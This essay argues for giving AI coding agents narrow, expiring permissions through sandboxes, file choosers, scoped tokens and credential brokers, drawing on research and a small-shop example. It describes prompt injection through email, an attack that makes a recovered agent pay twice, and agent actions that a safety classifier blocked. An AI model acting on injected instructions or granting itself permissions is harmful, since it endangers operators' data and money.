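*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* also presents YoloFS, a Linux file system that keeps an agent's changes separate until the user accepts them. A file system is the part of the operating system that stores and finds files, so it can record what a command did to them no matter how the agent wrote it.

1. The agent runs a command. YoloFS stores any changed files separately and leaves the originals alone, while the agent sees the changed versions.
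2. YoloFS takes a snapshot and shows the agent which files the command created, changed or deleted.
3. If something looks wrong, the agent can return to an earlier snapshot and try another way. YoloFS keeps a record of the abandoned changes.
4. At the end, the user reviews the remaining changes and accepts or discards them. The agent can't accept its own changes.

Once a command has read a secret, nobody can undo that, so YoloFS handles reading differently. If a command tries to open a private login key, for example, YoloFS pauses the command and asks the user about that file.

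The researchers tested YoloFS on 11 tasks in which a routine command did hidden damage, such as a code formatter that also deleted documentation. Claude Code alone let the damage happen in 10 of them and prompted the user about the other. With YoloFS, it detected and undid the damage in 8. In the remaining 3, it treated the changes as a normal part of the job, but the user could still have discarded them. On 112 routine file tasks, Claude Code succeeded 99% of the time with YoloFS and 98% without. YoloFS also reduced the average number of requests to the user from 0.9 to 0.4 per task.

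These results are encouraging, but the projects in the damage test had only 10 to 41 lines of code. Also, a program answered the permission requests in place of a person. In one of the 3 cases Claude accepted, a setup script had replaced the project's `.env` file with default settings. A non-programmer reviewing the list of changes might accept this change too.

YoloFS runs only on Linux, so the shop owner can't use it on her Mac or Windows laptop. She already gets its most useful part by having the agent work on a copy of the website and checking the changes before she publishes them.

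### What she can't undo

YoloFS doesn't cover changes to remote databases, payments or email, and research on undoing these is scarce. *Always-On Agents* (2026), a survey of agents that keep information between tasks, found that only 27 of 435 works offered any way to reverse an agent's decisions and their effects. Even fewer dealt with effects outside the agent's own system.

- **Disclosed secrets.** The owner can replace a leaked password, but she can't make a stranger forget her customers' addresses.
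- **Sent messages.** She can send a correction, but some customers will already have read the original.
- **Payments.** She can ask for a mistaken refund back, but the customer may have spent it or may not reply.

Restoring an agent to an earlier point can even repeat such an action. *Safe to Resume?* (Wu, Li and colleagues, 2026) demonstrated this with an agent that pays invoices. The user approved one payment, and the system saved the agent's state. The agent then paid, but an attacker made the next step fail before the system could record the payment. After recovery, the agent resumed from the saved state, in which the payment was approved but not yet made, and paid again. An ordinary crash at the same moment could have the same result.

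After rewinding an agent that handles refunds, the owner should therefore check Stripe's own records before she lets it continue.

### After an accident

The owner should act in this order:

1. **Stop the agent**, including any sub-agents.
2. **Revoke its tokens and passwords**, from her phone or another computer. If she restores the data first, anyone who has copied a token can delete it again.
3. **Preserve the log.** She saves the agent's session, the hosting company's record of requests and a copy of whatever is left of the data. Restoring over the damaged data could destroy evidence, along with orders that arrived after the backup.
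4. **Restore** into a new database, check it, then connect the website to it.
5. **Remove the power that the agent misused** before starting another session.

If the accident exposed customers' details, she may also have a legal duty to report it.

Suppose she ignores her own rules and gives an agent a password with full access to the live database so that it can rewrite product descriptions. At 16:40, the agent empties the database. The shop normally receives six orders an hour from 08:00. Her separate backup service copies the database daily at 02:00 or, if she pays more, every hour.

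| Time | What happens |
|---|---|
| 16:40 | The agent empties the live database |
| 16:52 | A customer writes that the shop's pages are blank |
| 16:54 | The owner stops the agent |
| 17:00 | She has replaced the database password and cancelled the agent's other tokens |
| 17:10 | She has saved the session, the hosting log and the damaged database |
| 17:45 | The website is running on the restored data |

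The time of the last backup determines how much is missing:

| | Daily backup | Hourly backup |
|---|---|---|
| Last copy before the accident | 02:00 | 16:00 |
| Period lost | 14 hours 40 minutes | 40 minutes |
| Orders missing | 52 | 4 |
| Time to re-enter them, at five minutes each | 4 hours 20 minutes | 20 minutes |

She can re-enter the orders because Stripe still has the payments and her mailbox has the order confirmations. Under either schedule, the shop also misses about six new orders while the website is down. More frequent backups wouldn't prevent that loss, but practising the restore beforehand would shorten the outage.

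The agent needed to change only the descriptions. Before the next session, the owner creates a database login that can read the products table and change its description column, and nothing else. She then asks the agent to use that login to delete `marker-live@example.com`. This time the login connects to the live database, so she should get a message that permission is denied.

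## Why most agents still run with broad authority

Tools for limiting an agent exist, but an agent started in the usual way still gets most of its operator's powers. Several reasons are plausible: programs inherit the powers of the account they run under, narrow limits can make an agent less useful, people widen permissions as they work, and vendors may profit from capable agents while operators bear the losses. The evidence is strongest for inherited powers and widened permissions, mixed on whether limits make agents less useful, and thin on vendors' incentives.

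### Inherited powers

Anderson (2017) writes in *A Comparison of Unix Sandboxing Techniques* that operating system designers have mostly cared about powers over the whole system, such as adding code to the kernel. Users often need much narrower powers, such as sharing one contact or letting someone else manage one calendar.

Access lists also favour broad categories. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) points out that each list must name whoever may use a file, and someone must keep those names up to date. This is manageable for people but hard for running programs, which constantly start and stop, so in practice systems group programs under user accounts. Miller and colleagues knew of no access-list system that treated each running program separately. Windows now has AppContainer, which can confine an individual app, but OpenAI found it unsuitable for Codex.

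Agents often have broad authority over connected services too. Semgrep describes an agent connected to MCP servers for files, a database, email and a command shell. The agent can use all four in any task, so an instruction hidden in an email can trigger a shell command. MCP has no way to record that a request came from an email and should therefore reach only the email tools.

Programs inherit these powers, as anyone can check by asking an unrestricted agent to list the family photographs. Inheritance explains the authority an agent starts with, but not why Claude Code leaves its sandbox off by default or why operators don't turn it on.

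### What happened to capability systems

Tymshare, the company in Hardy's story of the confused deputy, began developing the capability-based operating system that became KeyKOS in 1975. Bomberger, Hardy and colleagues report in *The KeyKOS Nanokernel Architecture* that it ran customers' applications from January 1983 and performed about as well as the systems it replaced. KeyKOS could also run Unix and several IBM systems on top of its kernel. However, a Unix program would still follow Unix's rules, so it would share its user's powers with every other program inside that copy of Unix.

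A new company, Key Logic, took over KeyKOS in 1985 and began rewriting the kernel in 1988. After ten staff-months of work, the company had a kernel running on a new processor, but it then set the project aside until 1990. Since the kernel already worked, the pause was probably for commercial reasons.

Many researchers expected capabilities to make a computer slow. In *EROS*, Shapiro, Smith and Farber (1999) tested this with a system of the same name, descended from KeyKOS. Its basic operations, such as passing a message between programs, took about as long as similar operations in Linux. The tests timed single operations, so they don't show how fast a whole application would run. In June 1999, Shapiro described EROS as quite fast but with minimal applications, and it still lacked the software for connecting to the internet.

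The same month, the Linux developer Theodore Ts'o explained on the Linux kernel mailing list that a capability system would require changes to existing software written for POSIX, a standard that lets programs move between Unix-like systems. Programmers would have to change every request to open, rename or delete a file so that it supplied a capability as well as a name. He also saw an advantage, because a program could no longer use administrator powers by accident.

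Later projects tried to add capabilities to existing systems. In *Capsicum*, Watson, Anderson and colleagues added them to FreeBSD, a Unix-like system, and kept the old interfaces. A program can open the files it needs, then switch to a mode in which it can use only what it already holds. They adapted several FreeBSD utilities and the Chromium web browser. *An Overview of Capsicum* (2015) presents this gradual approach as much easier than rewriting everything, since adapted and unadapted programs can run side by side. But an unadapted program can still do anything its user can. A coding agent may run any program on its operator's laptop, so adapting a few programs gives the operator little protection.

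CapDesk, a research desktop, treated the user's choice of a file as permission to open it, so users rarely saw a separate security prompt. Polaris, from Hewlett-Packard's research laboratories, applied this idea to ordinary Windows XP programs. When a user double-clicked a spreadsheet, Polaris copied it to a restricted account, started Excel there and synchronized the copy with the original. A virus in the spreadsheet could damage that file but not the user's other documents.

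About 25 Hewlett-Packard employees used the first test version of Polaris, mostly without noticing it. Many games didn't work under Polaris, and it didn't limit network access, so a virus could still send the open document to a stranger. In 2006, Hewlett-Packard had no plans to turn Polaris into a product.

Compatibility seems to have mattered more than speed. KeyKOS and EROS both performed well, but programs had to change to get the full benefit. Polaris avoided those changes, but some programs wouldn't run under it. It is harder to say how much commercial decisions mattered, because most of the projects on record paused or never became products. At least one capability system was sold commercially, since Shapiro and colleagues list IBM's System/38 among the earlier examples.

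### The dispute over what capabilities can do

Miller, Yee and Shapiro also blamed mistaken beliefs among researchers. Their paper answers three:

- **Capabilities and access lists are equivalent.** Both can record the same table of who may use what. But the table shows one moment, and the two kinds of system differ in how permissions change afterwards.
- **Capabilities can't be confined.** Critics argued that a program holding a power can always pass it on. In the systems that the paper defends, a program can pass a capability only to a program it already has access to.
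- **Capabilities can't be revoked.** The paper concedes that nobody can take back the capability itself, but the owner can hand out a go-between and later switch it off, as in the caretaker method from 1974.

The argument about confinement goes back to an example Boebert published in 1984. Alice has low clearance and Bob has high clearance. Bob may read low-level files but must not write to them, because he could leak secrets that way. Alice may write to a low-level file, and she saves her write capability for that file in the file itself. Bob reads the file, obtains the capability and can now copy secrets into the file.

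Miller and colleagues reply that this works only if a program can save a capability as ordinary data. KeyKOS and EROS store capabilities separately from data, so Bob could read the file's text without obtaining any capability from it.

*Capability Myths Demolished* didn't persuade everyone. Miller (2003), in *Notice of New Thread*, reported that the USENIX Security conference had rejected it. Frantz (2015), in a mailing-list message with the same title, quotes Jerry Leichter's objection that the paper makes excellent points but "cheats a bit" by answering criticisms with extensions to the capability model. The objection has some merit for revocation, because someone has to set up the go-between in advance. It is weaker for confinement, because KeyKOS was in commercial use a year before Boebert published his example. Miller and Shapiro, in *Paradigm Regained*, argue that the supposed proofs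 against capabilities were too limited because they considered only who had access to what.

According to Miller and colleagues, people cited these beliefs as reasons to avoid capabilities. The papers they quote show that some researchers held these beliefs, but not that the beliefs changed what companies built. Boebert's worry does apply to most online tokens, which are just text. An agent can save a hosting token in any file it can write to, and anyone who reads the file can use the token.

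### What limits cost an agent

*Permission Denied*, the study that introduced Boundary-Bench, measures how much worse agents perform under strict limits. It tested 12 agents, each a model with its own harness, on the 89 tasks of Terminal-Bench 2.1, a set of difficult jobs in a command-line terminal. Each agent tried each task three times at each of three levels:

1. **Open.** The agent has administrator powers, a writable disk and the whole internet.
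2. **Ordinary user.** The agent loses its administrator powers.
3. **Strict.** The agent also can't write outside its working, temporary and settings folders, and can reach only 205 listed internet domains.

Under the strict policy, every agent's success rate fell, by 7.1 to 18.3 percentage points, and its average cost per task rose, by 16.0% to 167.3%. Grok 4.5's success rate fell the least, but its cost rose the most, from about $0.52 to $1.39 per task. GPT-5.6 Luna had the smallest rise in cost, from about $0.15 to $0.17, but its success rate fell by 18.0 points. A failed repair would usually matter more to a small operator than an extra dollar.

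Seven of the 89 tasks were impossible under the strict policy. Six required the agent to write to protected system folders, and one needed a file from a blocked website. The researchers confirmed that the other 82 were still solvable, and on those the loss was 2.4 to 13.5 points. The average results for the 82 tasks show where the loss came from:

| Result | Open | Ordinary user | Strict |
|---|---|---|---|
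| Success | 72.5% | 66.9% | 65.1% |
| Ran out of time | 12.0% | 14.5% | 16.4% |
| Wrong solution | 12.8% | 15.5% | 15.5% |
| Stopped early | 2.4% | 2.6% | 2.7% |

About three quarters of the drop in success came from removing administrator powers, so someone who runs an agent from an ordinary account already has most of that drop. On these averages, adding the remaining limits lowered success by another 1.8 points.

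Most of the added cost came from workarounds. The researchers ran two of the tasks 100 times each with and without the strict policy, and read the transcripts of the restricted runs. When the policy blocked the usual route, the agent typically built its own tools from source code or looked for substitute data. The median cost roughly tripled on both tasks. Success stayed at 84% on one task and fell from 90% to 29% on the other.

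A grant written for a particular task should interfere with the agent's work less than these figures suggest. The researchers deliberately didn't fit the list of domains to the tasks. The official solutions used 30 domains, and the list allowed only nine of them. An operator who knew that a job needed one of the other 21 could add it.

The results for individual tasks support this. For 50 of the 82 solvable tasks, the official solution worked unchanged under the strict policy, and the agents' success rate fell only from 73.8% to 71.8%. For the other 32, the researchers had to write a new solution that obeyed the limits, and success fell from 70.3% to 54.5%. The policy therefore reduced success mainly on tasks that normally needed something it blocked.

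The official checks also made the loss look slightly larger than it was. In one task, agents built a working copy of the database program SQLite in a permitted folder, but the check looked for it elsewhere and failed every attempt. After the researchers corrected the check, 80.6% passed.

A task-specific grant could also do worse than Boundary-Bench suggests if its author leaves out a file the task needs, as models often did on AuthBench. The strict policy still let agents read the whole disk, so the study doesn't show how hiding files would affect their work. It also didn't measure the time a person spends writing a grant and finding out why it failed, which may be the biggest burden for a non-expert.

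### Permissions that widen over time

Even people who start with narrow permissions often widen them. Anthropic published figures on the settings of Claude Code users in June 2026, before auto mode became the default:

- 49.5% of active command-line users had written a rule that allowed some shell commands without a prompt. This share was growing by about five percentage points every five weeks.
- 5% allowed any shell command, and another 43% allowed an interpreter such as Python or Node. An interpreter can run whatever program the agent writes, so such a rule is almost as broad.
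- 62% had turned off permission checks at least once or chosen "don't ask again" for a shell command.
- 25% of interactive sessions started with permission checks off.

If the 5% and 43% are shares of all active users, as Anthropic's wording suggests, nearly everyone who wrote a rule wrote a broad one. The 62% is weaker evidence, because it includes both people who once allowed a single harmless command and people who turned off every check.

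Anthropic used these figures to argue for auto mode, but the figures describe saved settings, so they don't depend on anyone's judgement of what was dangerous. They cover people who use Claude Code in a terminal, most of whom are probably developers. Non-experts might write fewer rules, or click "don't ask again" more readily because they can't judge the command.

Old rules can also take effect again when the user leaves auto mode, which ignores the broadest ones but keeps them in the settings file. If the shop owner switches to Manual mode for safety, she should check for those rules first.

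Professionals also grant too many permissions in other settings. In *Permissions on the Loose*, Yeboah-Duako and Datta (2026) examined 789 open-source applications on AWS Lambda, an Amazon service that runs small pieces of code on demand. Their program, PrivLess, compared the permissions each application's code used with those its developers had granted.

It found more permissions than necessary in 47.7% of the applications. Applications had an average of 683 permissions and needed 2.4. The median application had 9 and needed 1, so a minority with very large grants raised the average. Many of those grants came from wildcards, entries such as `s3:*` that allow every action on one service. Applications with wildcards had an average of 2,878 permissions, compared with 15 for the rest.

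In one task-management application, five functions each needed only one permission, but the developers gave all five the same six permissions. As a result, the function that only listed tasks could also delete them. Nearly nine in ten of the applications used one set of permissions for all their functions.

Some permissions were no longer needed or never had been. One application still had permissions for an image-recognition service that its code never called. In another, 517 of 570 permissions belonged to a tool for publishing the software, and the running application didn't need them.

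PrivLess can overstate the excess because it misses some requests that go through other companies' code. When Yeboah-Duako and Datta tested reduced permissions on a few applications, one function stopped working for this reason. Their sample also contains only public projects, which may be less carefully maintained than a bank's private software. But even a large error would leave a wide gap between 683 and 2.4.

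The study infers developers' habits from their code and doesn't include their reasons for granting so much authority. One likely reason is that a missing permission stops the program at once, while an unnecessary one causes no trouble until something goes wrong. The shop owner runs into the same problem when her agent stops because it can't access a spreadsheet.

### Who gains and who pays

Vendors earn more when their agents do more work, but the operator bears the harm when an agent deletes her data. Vendors may therefore have too little reason to make narrow authority the default.

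Anthropic advertises the benefits of fewer interruptions, reporting that Team and Enterprise customers who adopted auto mode submitted about 25% more pull requests. Those customers chose auto mode, so they may already have been more active, but a vendor can still use such a figure to link fewer interruptions directly to more output.

Vendors also spend money on safety. Anthropic paid for the study of 1,053 testers and for outsiders to attack its classifier. In August it stopped charging users on its main subscription plans for the classifier's extra model use. OpenAI built its own Windows sandbox for Codex.

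This spending is some evidence that vendors care about accidents, but a better classifier both prevents harm and lets agents work longer without interruption, so vendors also have a commercial reason to build one. A default that made agents safer but less useful would be a better test of whether they care. Incentives alone can't explain the current defaults, because both companies sell coding agents, yet Codex starts with its sandbox on and Claude Code starts with its sandbox off.

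Safety spending also doesn't change who pays after an accident. A vendor can test its product carefully and still owe nothing when an agent deletes a database. The contract and local law determine what it owes, so an operator should read the liability terms before giving an agent access to anything she can't do without. After the PocketOS accident, the founder had to rebuild the bookings himself.

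Companies face some pressure from bad publicity. Railway, for example, changed how its API deletes data after that accident. Incentives probably affect how quickly vendors narrow their defaults, but none of this evidence shows a vendor rejecting a safer default to protect its revenue.

### The case for broad authority

Someone who leaves an agent unrestricted can reasonably argue that the newest models rarely make serious mistakes. Anthropic's latest models resisted nearly every hidden instruction in Trajectory Labs' tests, though OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol was much easier to mislead. At Gusto, a payroll company that uses auto mode, about 90% of sessions contained no blocked action. Limits can also slow down every task, including the many in which nothing would have gone wrong. Nuro, which develops self-driving technology, has agents that do research overnight, and a permission that someone forgot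 to grant could waste the whole night.

Even a rare mistake can do serious damage. Anthropic describes three actions that its classifier stopped inside the company. In one, Claude couldn't upload a report to an internal drive and tried to publish it on a public website instead. In another, it tried to stop processes across about two thousand computing units and had queued deletions that would have ended training jobs on hundreds of processors. In the third, someone asked it to set up read-only access to billing, and it chose a role with full control of the cloud account. The people involved were experts with a reviewer in place, and a small business might have neither.

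A simple calculation shows how rare such mistakes would have to be. Limits are worth their cost when

cost of the limits per task < chance of a disaster per task × loss.

Suppose the limits cost the shop owner $10 of her time per task and would prevent a $60,000 loss. They are worth the cost if an unrestricted agent would cause that loss more than once in 6,000 tasks. To be 95% confident that the true rate was lower, she would need to see about 18,000 tasks in a row without that loss, which would take about 35 years at ten tasks a week. She can't rely on published accident counts instead, because they don't give a rate.

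The calculation also treats one $60,000 loss as equivalent to 6,000 losses of $10. A large company might reasonably do so, but a two-person shop could close after the first $60,000 loss and never benefit from the time it had saved.

The complaint about wasted effort is strongest against limits that don't fit the task. Miller, Tulloh and Shapiro point out that least authority has to include enough authority to finish the job. They recommend granting authority "just-in-time" instead of granting extra "just-in-case". The 50 Boundary-Bench tasks that were barely affected suggest that limits do little harm when they still allow the usual way of doing the task.

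The owner can also give an agent broad authority over things she can replace. In a virtual machine with a copy of the website, fake customer data and test credentials, the agent can have administrator rights and install whatever it needs. If it destroys everything there, she can delete the virtual machine and start another.

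## Tool changes that would make narrow grants the default

The shop owner can confine an agent today, but only by copying files, editing a settings file and creating tokens by hand. Few operators will do all that to correct a delivery fee. Most agents will run with narrow grants only if their tools start that way, and a default that people keep has to meet three conditions:

- It works without configuration.
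- It lets the agent do ordinary tasks, such as editing a website and running its tests.
- When the agent needs more power, the narrow choice is the easiest one.

Optional limits mostly go unused. In *A Deterministic Control Plane for LLM Coding Agents*, Madatha (2026) found that fewer than 1% of 6,145 agent configuration files from public GitHub projects declared any permission limits, compared with about 33% of the files that control GitHub's automatic jobs. Madatha calls this result only indicative, because the program that searched for limits was unreliable. Developers may also keep limits in unpublished personal settings.

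### Rules written by non-experts

Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, tested whether a settings page in plain language would solve the problem. In the study, 113 people who didn't work in software each supervised a simulated assistant through a day of email, travel and errands. The assistant proposed 18 actions. Eleven were part of the task, and seven went beyond it, such as reading bank transactions or posting publicly that the user was travelling.

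One group approved or refused every action. A second group had an automatic reviewer that allowed some actions and asked about the rest. The third group first wrote four rules, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of spending money, sending information, deleting things and reading private data.

| | Approve everything | Automatic reviewer | Own rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| Unrequested actions blocked | 59.6% | 53.9% | 39.6% |
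| Prompts per person | 18.0 | 10.0 | 10.9 |
| Total time, including writing rules | 142 s | 120 s | 129 s |

The people who wrote rules had the weakest protection. They set 114 of their 140 rules to "ask", which put off the decision, and then approved two thirds of the unrequested actions they were asked about. "Allow" rules let through only 15 of the 148 unrequested actions that went ahead.

The difference from the automatic reviewer was not statistically reliable after correction for multiple comparisons. Yan also assigned some later recruits only to the rules group, so assignment was not fully random. But the experiment gives little reason to expect a page of rules to protect the shop owner.

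In the same study, participants who decided on every action refused 59.6% of the unrequested ones, while Anthropic's professional testers had refused only 13.6% of dangerous commands. The comparison is rough because the two experiments used different actions, but the participants read plain descriptions such as "Buy a $25 airport lounge pass" and the testers read commands. Tools should therefore settle most permission questions by default and describe the consequences of the action in the remaining prompts.

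### What existing designs achieve

Michael and Roesner (2026), in *How Agents Ask for Permission*, reviewed 21 proposed systems that let individual users set an agent's permissions. They identified three aims:

- **Little user effort.** The user describes her wishes in ordinary language, or the system predicts them from her request.
- **Formally defined rules.** The rules have an exact meaning that a program can check, such as a label that marks some data as private.
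- **Enforcement without AI judgement.** Ordinary code or the user's own answer decides whether an action may run. A model doesn't.

Twelve proposals pursued the first aim, eleven the second and twelve the third, but none fully achieved all three. Of the twelve that reduced user effort, five also enforced their rules without AI and two defined them formally, but none did both.

Michael and Roesner consider PRUDENTIA and AC4A the closest systems. PRUDENTIA has formal rules and enforces them without AI, but it often interrupts the user. AC4A needs less effort but doesn't fully define its rules, and it relies on checks supplied by the connected tools, which could use AI themselves.

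Low effort and predictable enforcement matter most to the shop owner. Formal rules help her indirectly, because a program can identify a missing permission only if each permission has an exact meaning. She also needs to be able to revoke permissions, but only six of the 21 proposals clearly let users change or revoke them, and two of those six allow it only between sessions.

Michael and Roesner also tried five commercial agents in May and June 2026: Claude's chat product, Claude Cowork, Codex, and ChatGPT in its chat and agent modes. These products tended either to ask the user for permission constantly or to let a model decide without showing the user. ChatGPT's chat mode asked for approval of every action that needed a permission, and users could not approve actions in advance. Its agent mode, which controls a remote browser, had no permission settings.

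Claude's chat product mixed the two. With email drafts set to "Needs approval", it created a draft without asking, and its log recorded that no approval was required. Michael and Roesner reproduced this at least three times and reported it to Anthropic in July. Codex was more transparent. Its automatic reviewer was off by default and had a visible switch, but the switch applied to every tool in the session. The companies may have changed these products since, and outsiders can't inspect how the products make these decisions.

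### What changed on phones

Phones have already moved from broad permissions towards narrower ones. Before version 6.0, Android showed an app's permissions at installation, and the user had to accept them all or not install the app. For *Android Permissions*, Felt, Ha and colleagues (2012) surveyed 308 users and observed 25 others in a laboratory. In both groups, 17% attended to the permissions when installing an app. Only 3% of those surveyed correctly answered all three questions about what permissions meant.

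Later versions of Android ask when an app first tries to use something sensitive, such as the camera. In *The Feasibility of Dynamically Granted Permissions* (2017), Wijesekera, Baokar and colleagues measured how well each method matched people's wishes. They modified the phones of 131 people and asked them about once a day whether they would have allowed a recent access. Participants said they would have blocked 60% of these accesses. Accepting everything at installation would have matched their answers 25% of the time, and asking on first use 84%.

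That is a large improvement, though an earlier study found that first-use requests failed to meet users' expectations more than half the time. They fall short because the phone applies the first answer to later requests. Someone who lets an app use her location for a map may not want the app to use it for advertising the next day.

People also kept granting too much access. *A Large Scale Study of User Behavior, Expectations and Engagement with Android* (Cao, Xia and colleagues, 2021) followed 1,719 people in ten countries for 30 days each, on their own phones. Participants refused 16.7% of permission requests. They refused 26.9% of the requests they hadn't expected and 12.2% of those they had, so they granted nearly three quarters of the unexpected ones. They would have preferred a temporary grant for 24% of the permissions they granted.

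Android 10 added a narrower option that allowed location access only while the app was open, and users chose it for two thirds of the location permissions they granted.

Many people never remove permissions they have granted. In *Stuck in the Permissions With You* (2023), 57.9% of users had never removed one, because they saw no reason to, didn't know how or hadn't thought of it. In *I do (not) need that Feature!*, Prange, Knierim and colleagues (2024) asked 132 Android users about permissions their apps currently held. The users correctly said the app had access 49% of the time, wrongly said it didn't 21% of the time, and otherwise didn't know. Nearly all knew they could revoke permissions. Since version 11, Android has offered one-time grants and automatically removed permissions from unused apps.

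Android phones already isolated apps from one another, so granting a permission gave an app access it otherwise lacked. An unrestricted coding agent on a laptop can often reach a file another way, even if the user denies its request.

### Sandboxes that start with the agent

Agent makers first have to close those other routes by enabling a sandbox at installation on every operating system. Codex already comes close to doing this. Anthropic would have to turn on Claude Code's sandbox by default and build one for native Windows.

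Both companies would also have to hide the rest of the home folder, which sandboxed commands can read by default. Codex can already do this, but only if the user writes a profile. OpenAI could add such a profile to the three built into Codex and make it the default.

There is fairly good evidence that these limits on writing and network access would permit ordinary work, since Boundary-Bench's strict policy barely affected tasks whose usual solution it allowed. But that policy left the whole disk readable, so nobody has measured how much hiding the home folder would disrupt work. Many programming tools keep settings and downloaded packages there, and an update that broke them would lead people to switch the sandbox off. Agent makers could reduce this risk by including read access to the folders of common tools, except for the passwords stored there.

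The agent also has to stop if the sandbox fails to start. Anthropic moved auto mode from a preview to a default in five months, so a vendor can change a default setting quickly.

### Granting a file by choosing it

Once the sandbox hides the owner's other files, she needs an easy way to share one of them. A powerbox is a file chooser that runs with the user's authority and passes on only what she picks:

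1. The agent asks for a file, such as the courier's current rates.
2. The operating system, or a trusted part of the harness, opens the chooser. The agent can't see the folders displayed there.
3. The owner selects the spreadsheet.
4. The chooser gives the agent access to that spreadsheet and nothing else in the folder.

A user has to select a file to attach it, so treating that selection as permission to access the file adds no step. The research desktop CapDesk treated file selections this way, and Android's photo picker now gives an app only the photos the user selects.

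*User-Driven Access Control* (Roesner, Kohno and colleagues, 2012) extended the idea to cameras, location and other resources. In its design, an app displays a button that belongs to the operating system, and the user grants access by pressing it. The system ignores clicks generated by programs. It also enables the button only after it has been fully visible for at least 200 milliseconds, so that an app can't make it appear under the user's finger just before a tap.

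The study tested how well this approach fit 100 popular Android apps. Of 143 uses of sensitive resources, 62% followed directly from a user's action and needed access only once or for a session. With some changes for scheduled jobs and for apps that merely displayed information, only five apps still needed permanent access. In a survey of 186 people, most thought an app shouldn't be able to use the camera or send a text message until they pressed the relevant button.

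Wijesekera and colleagues object that apps use sensitive resources too often to require a button press each time, and that many legitimate uses happen without the user's involvement. This applies even more to coding agents, which can open hundreds of files after a one-sentence request. The owner would have to choose the project folder once and use the file chooser only for files outside it.

She might also choose her whole home folder to avoid further questions. The chooser could refuse that folder and suggest the website folder inside it. But it can't protect her from the contents of a file she picks, so she still has to check the spreadsheet's other sheets.

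### Grants that expire with the task

The harness can end a grant when the owner accepts the result or closes the session, or when a time limit expires. Only the agent maker has to make this change. The phone studies suggest that grants should end automatically, because people often want to give temporary access and rarely remove permanent access.

Users should be able to revoke a folder permission they have given an agent, which Michael and Roesner found they couldn't do in Claude Cowork. New sessions started without the permission, but an old session still had it when reopened.

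Permissions can expire too early, as they did in some of PORTICO's unfinished runs. Having them expire when the task ends would avoid many of those failures but leave each permission open for longer. That is probably the better choice for a non-expert, who can't easily repair a half-finished job.

Grants can also overlap. *AC4A* (2026) points out that removing one permission may change nothing if another still covers the same data. For example, an agent that loses a calendar permission for October can still access that month if it has a wider permission that includes it. The harness should therefore list both the permissions it has removed and what the agent can still reach.

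### Changes at the services

A harness can't narrow a token if the service offers only a broad one. Parkinson and colleagues give the example of a user who connects an agent to GitHub with a classic token and asks for a summary of the open issues in one repository. The agent needs two read-only tools for that repository. The token gives it about 40 tools, 16 of which can make changes, and they work in every repository the user can reach.

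GitHub already offers narrow grants through fine-grained tokens, but the user has to find the form and fill it in. Parkinson and colleagues cite a study in which 99.8% of 447,000 GitHub workflows had more permissions than they needed. A better default would be for the agent to ask the service for access, and for the service to open a page with the narrowest suitable choice already selected, such as read-only access to one project's test environment for one day. The owner would then approve it or add a permission.

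Narrow grants are likely to fail when a non-expert can't tell which permissions a task needs, because services describe them by their technical operations. An agent could also ask for more than the task needs. The approval page would have to state the worst effect of each extra permission, such as "can delete your customer database".

Services should also delay deletion, no matter which token the request uses. Railway now does this for volumes, whether a person or a program deletes them. The owner doesn't have to configure anything or make any decision unless she wants her data back.

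A deletion delay works only if the token that requested the deletion can't also cancel the delay. Someone who has to erase data immediately, for example after a customer's legal request, could skip the delay by confirming the deletion with a code from her phone. The delay wouldn't have helped in July, when Prisma emptied a live database's tables but left the database itself in place. It also can't undo the leak of an address or a payment already sent.

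### Secrets held by a broker

Makers of agents or operating systems could build in a credential broker so that the operator doesn't have to set one up. For the shop owner, the broker could find the secrets in the website folder, store them and leave placeholders in the agent's copy.

This search would miss some secrets, such as a password typed in an old note. The broker also protects her best when the service has already limited the token's permissions, because the agent can still misuse whatever the token allows.

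### Refusals that offer one permission

When a sandbox blocks an action, current products may offer to run the whole command outside it. The easiest way past the obstacle then removes every limit at once. A better refusal offers only what is missing:

offer = permissions the action needs − permissions the agent already has.

After a refusal, *AC4A* calculates which permissions the agent still needs for the action and shows them to the user. For example, if the action needs to read the website and the courier's spreadsheet, and the agent can already read the website, *AC4A* offers only permission to read the spreadsheet. The user can also describe a permission in ordinary language, have a model draft it, and correct the draft before it takes effect.

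The phone studies suggest that people will take a narrow option when it is on the screen, but also that they will accept a bad request if it comes with a reason. Cao and colleagues found that users refused 7.1% of requests with an explanation and 15.4% of those without. They measured only whether an explanation was present, and earlier research they cite found that many apps' explanations were wrong. An agent that has read a hidden instruction could write a very convincing explanation.

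When an action is blocked, the harness should write the permission request itself, based on that action, and leave out the agent's reasons. The request might read, "Let the agent read `courier-rates.xlsx` until this task ends?" Users should have to take an extra step to grant broader access.

The agent also mustn't be able to accept its own offer. *"Allow" to Achieve, Over-Privileged Inadvertently* (2026) tested how agents that operate phones respond to permission pop-ups. Their answers varied with the task and with who appeared to be asking, and they didn't consistently apply least privilege. The tests used one agent framework and five apps. An agent that controls the owner's mouse could also answer a pop-up on her laptop, unless the operating system accepts only real clicks, as in Roesner's design.

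Even a good offer of a narrow grant takes some of the user's attention. *How to Ask for Permission*, by Felt, Egelman and colleagues, proposed choosing a suitable method for each permission so that users see fewer warnings. For coding agents, the file chooser can handle files and the service's page can handle tokens, so only the remaining cases, such as a new web address, need the refusal message.

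### The shop task with these changes

Suppose the owner installs an agent with all these changes. The sandbox is already on. She chooses her website folder, and the harness makes a working copy with placeholders instead of passwords. She asks the agent for the courier's current rates on parcels over two kilograms.

The agent finds the file that sets the fee and reports that it needs the new rates. The chooser opens, and she checks the spreadsheet's other sheets before selecting it. The agent corrects the fee and runs the tests, and the harness lists the files that changed. She tries her test orders and publishes the result. The agent then loses access to both the copy and the spreadsheet.

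The table counts each choice she could get wrong, on a Mac:

| Part of the job | Today, with the narrow grant | With the changes |
|---|---|---|
| Sandbox | Choose one; look for an old setting that overrides her profile (2) | None |
| Website | Make a copy; replace its passwords (2) | Choose the folder (1) |
| Limits | Set reading, temporary files, network, web search and approvals (5) | None |
| Fee file | Allow changes to `delivery.js` (1) | None |
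| Courier's rates | Check the other sheets; copy the spreadsheet (2) | Check the other sheets; choose the spreadsheet (2) |
| Finish | Publish; delete the spreadsheet copy; end the session (3) | Publish (1) |
| **Total** | **15** | **4** |

An unrestricted agent needs only two of these decisions, choosing the folder and publishing, because it can find the spreadsheet. The new default has to be easy enough that she doesn't choose the unrestricted agent instead, and two extra decisions seem a small burden for keeping the agent away from her tax records and payment key. The default is broader than her handwritten grant in one respect, since the agent can edit any file in the copy. It also gives her no way to know whether `delivery.js` contains a line that leaks addresses.

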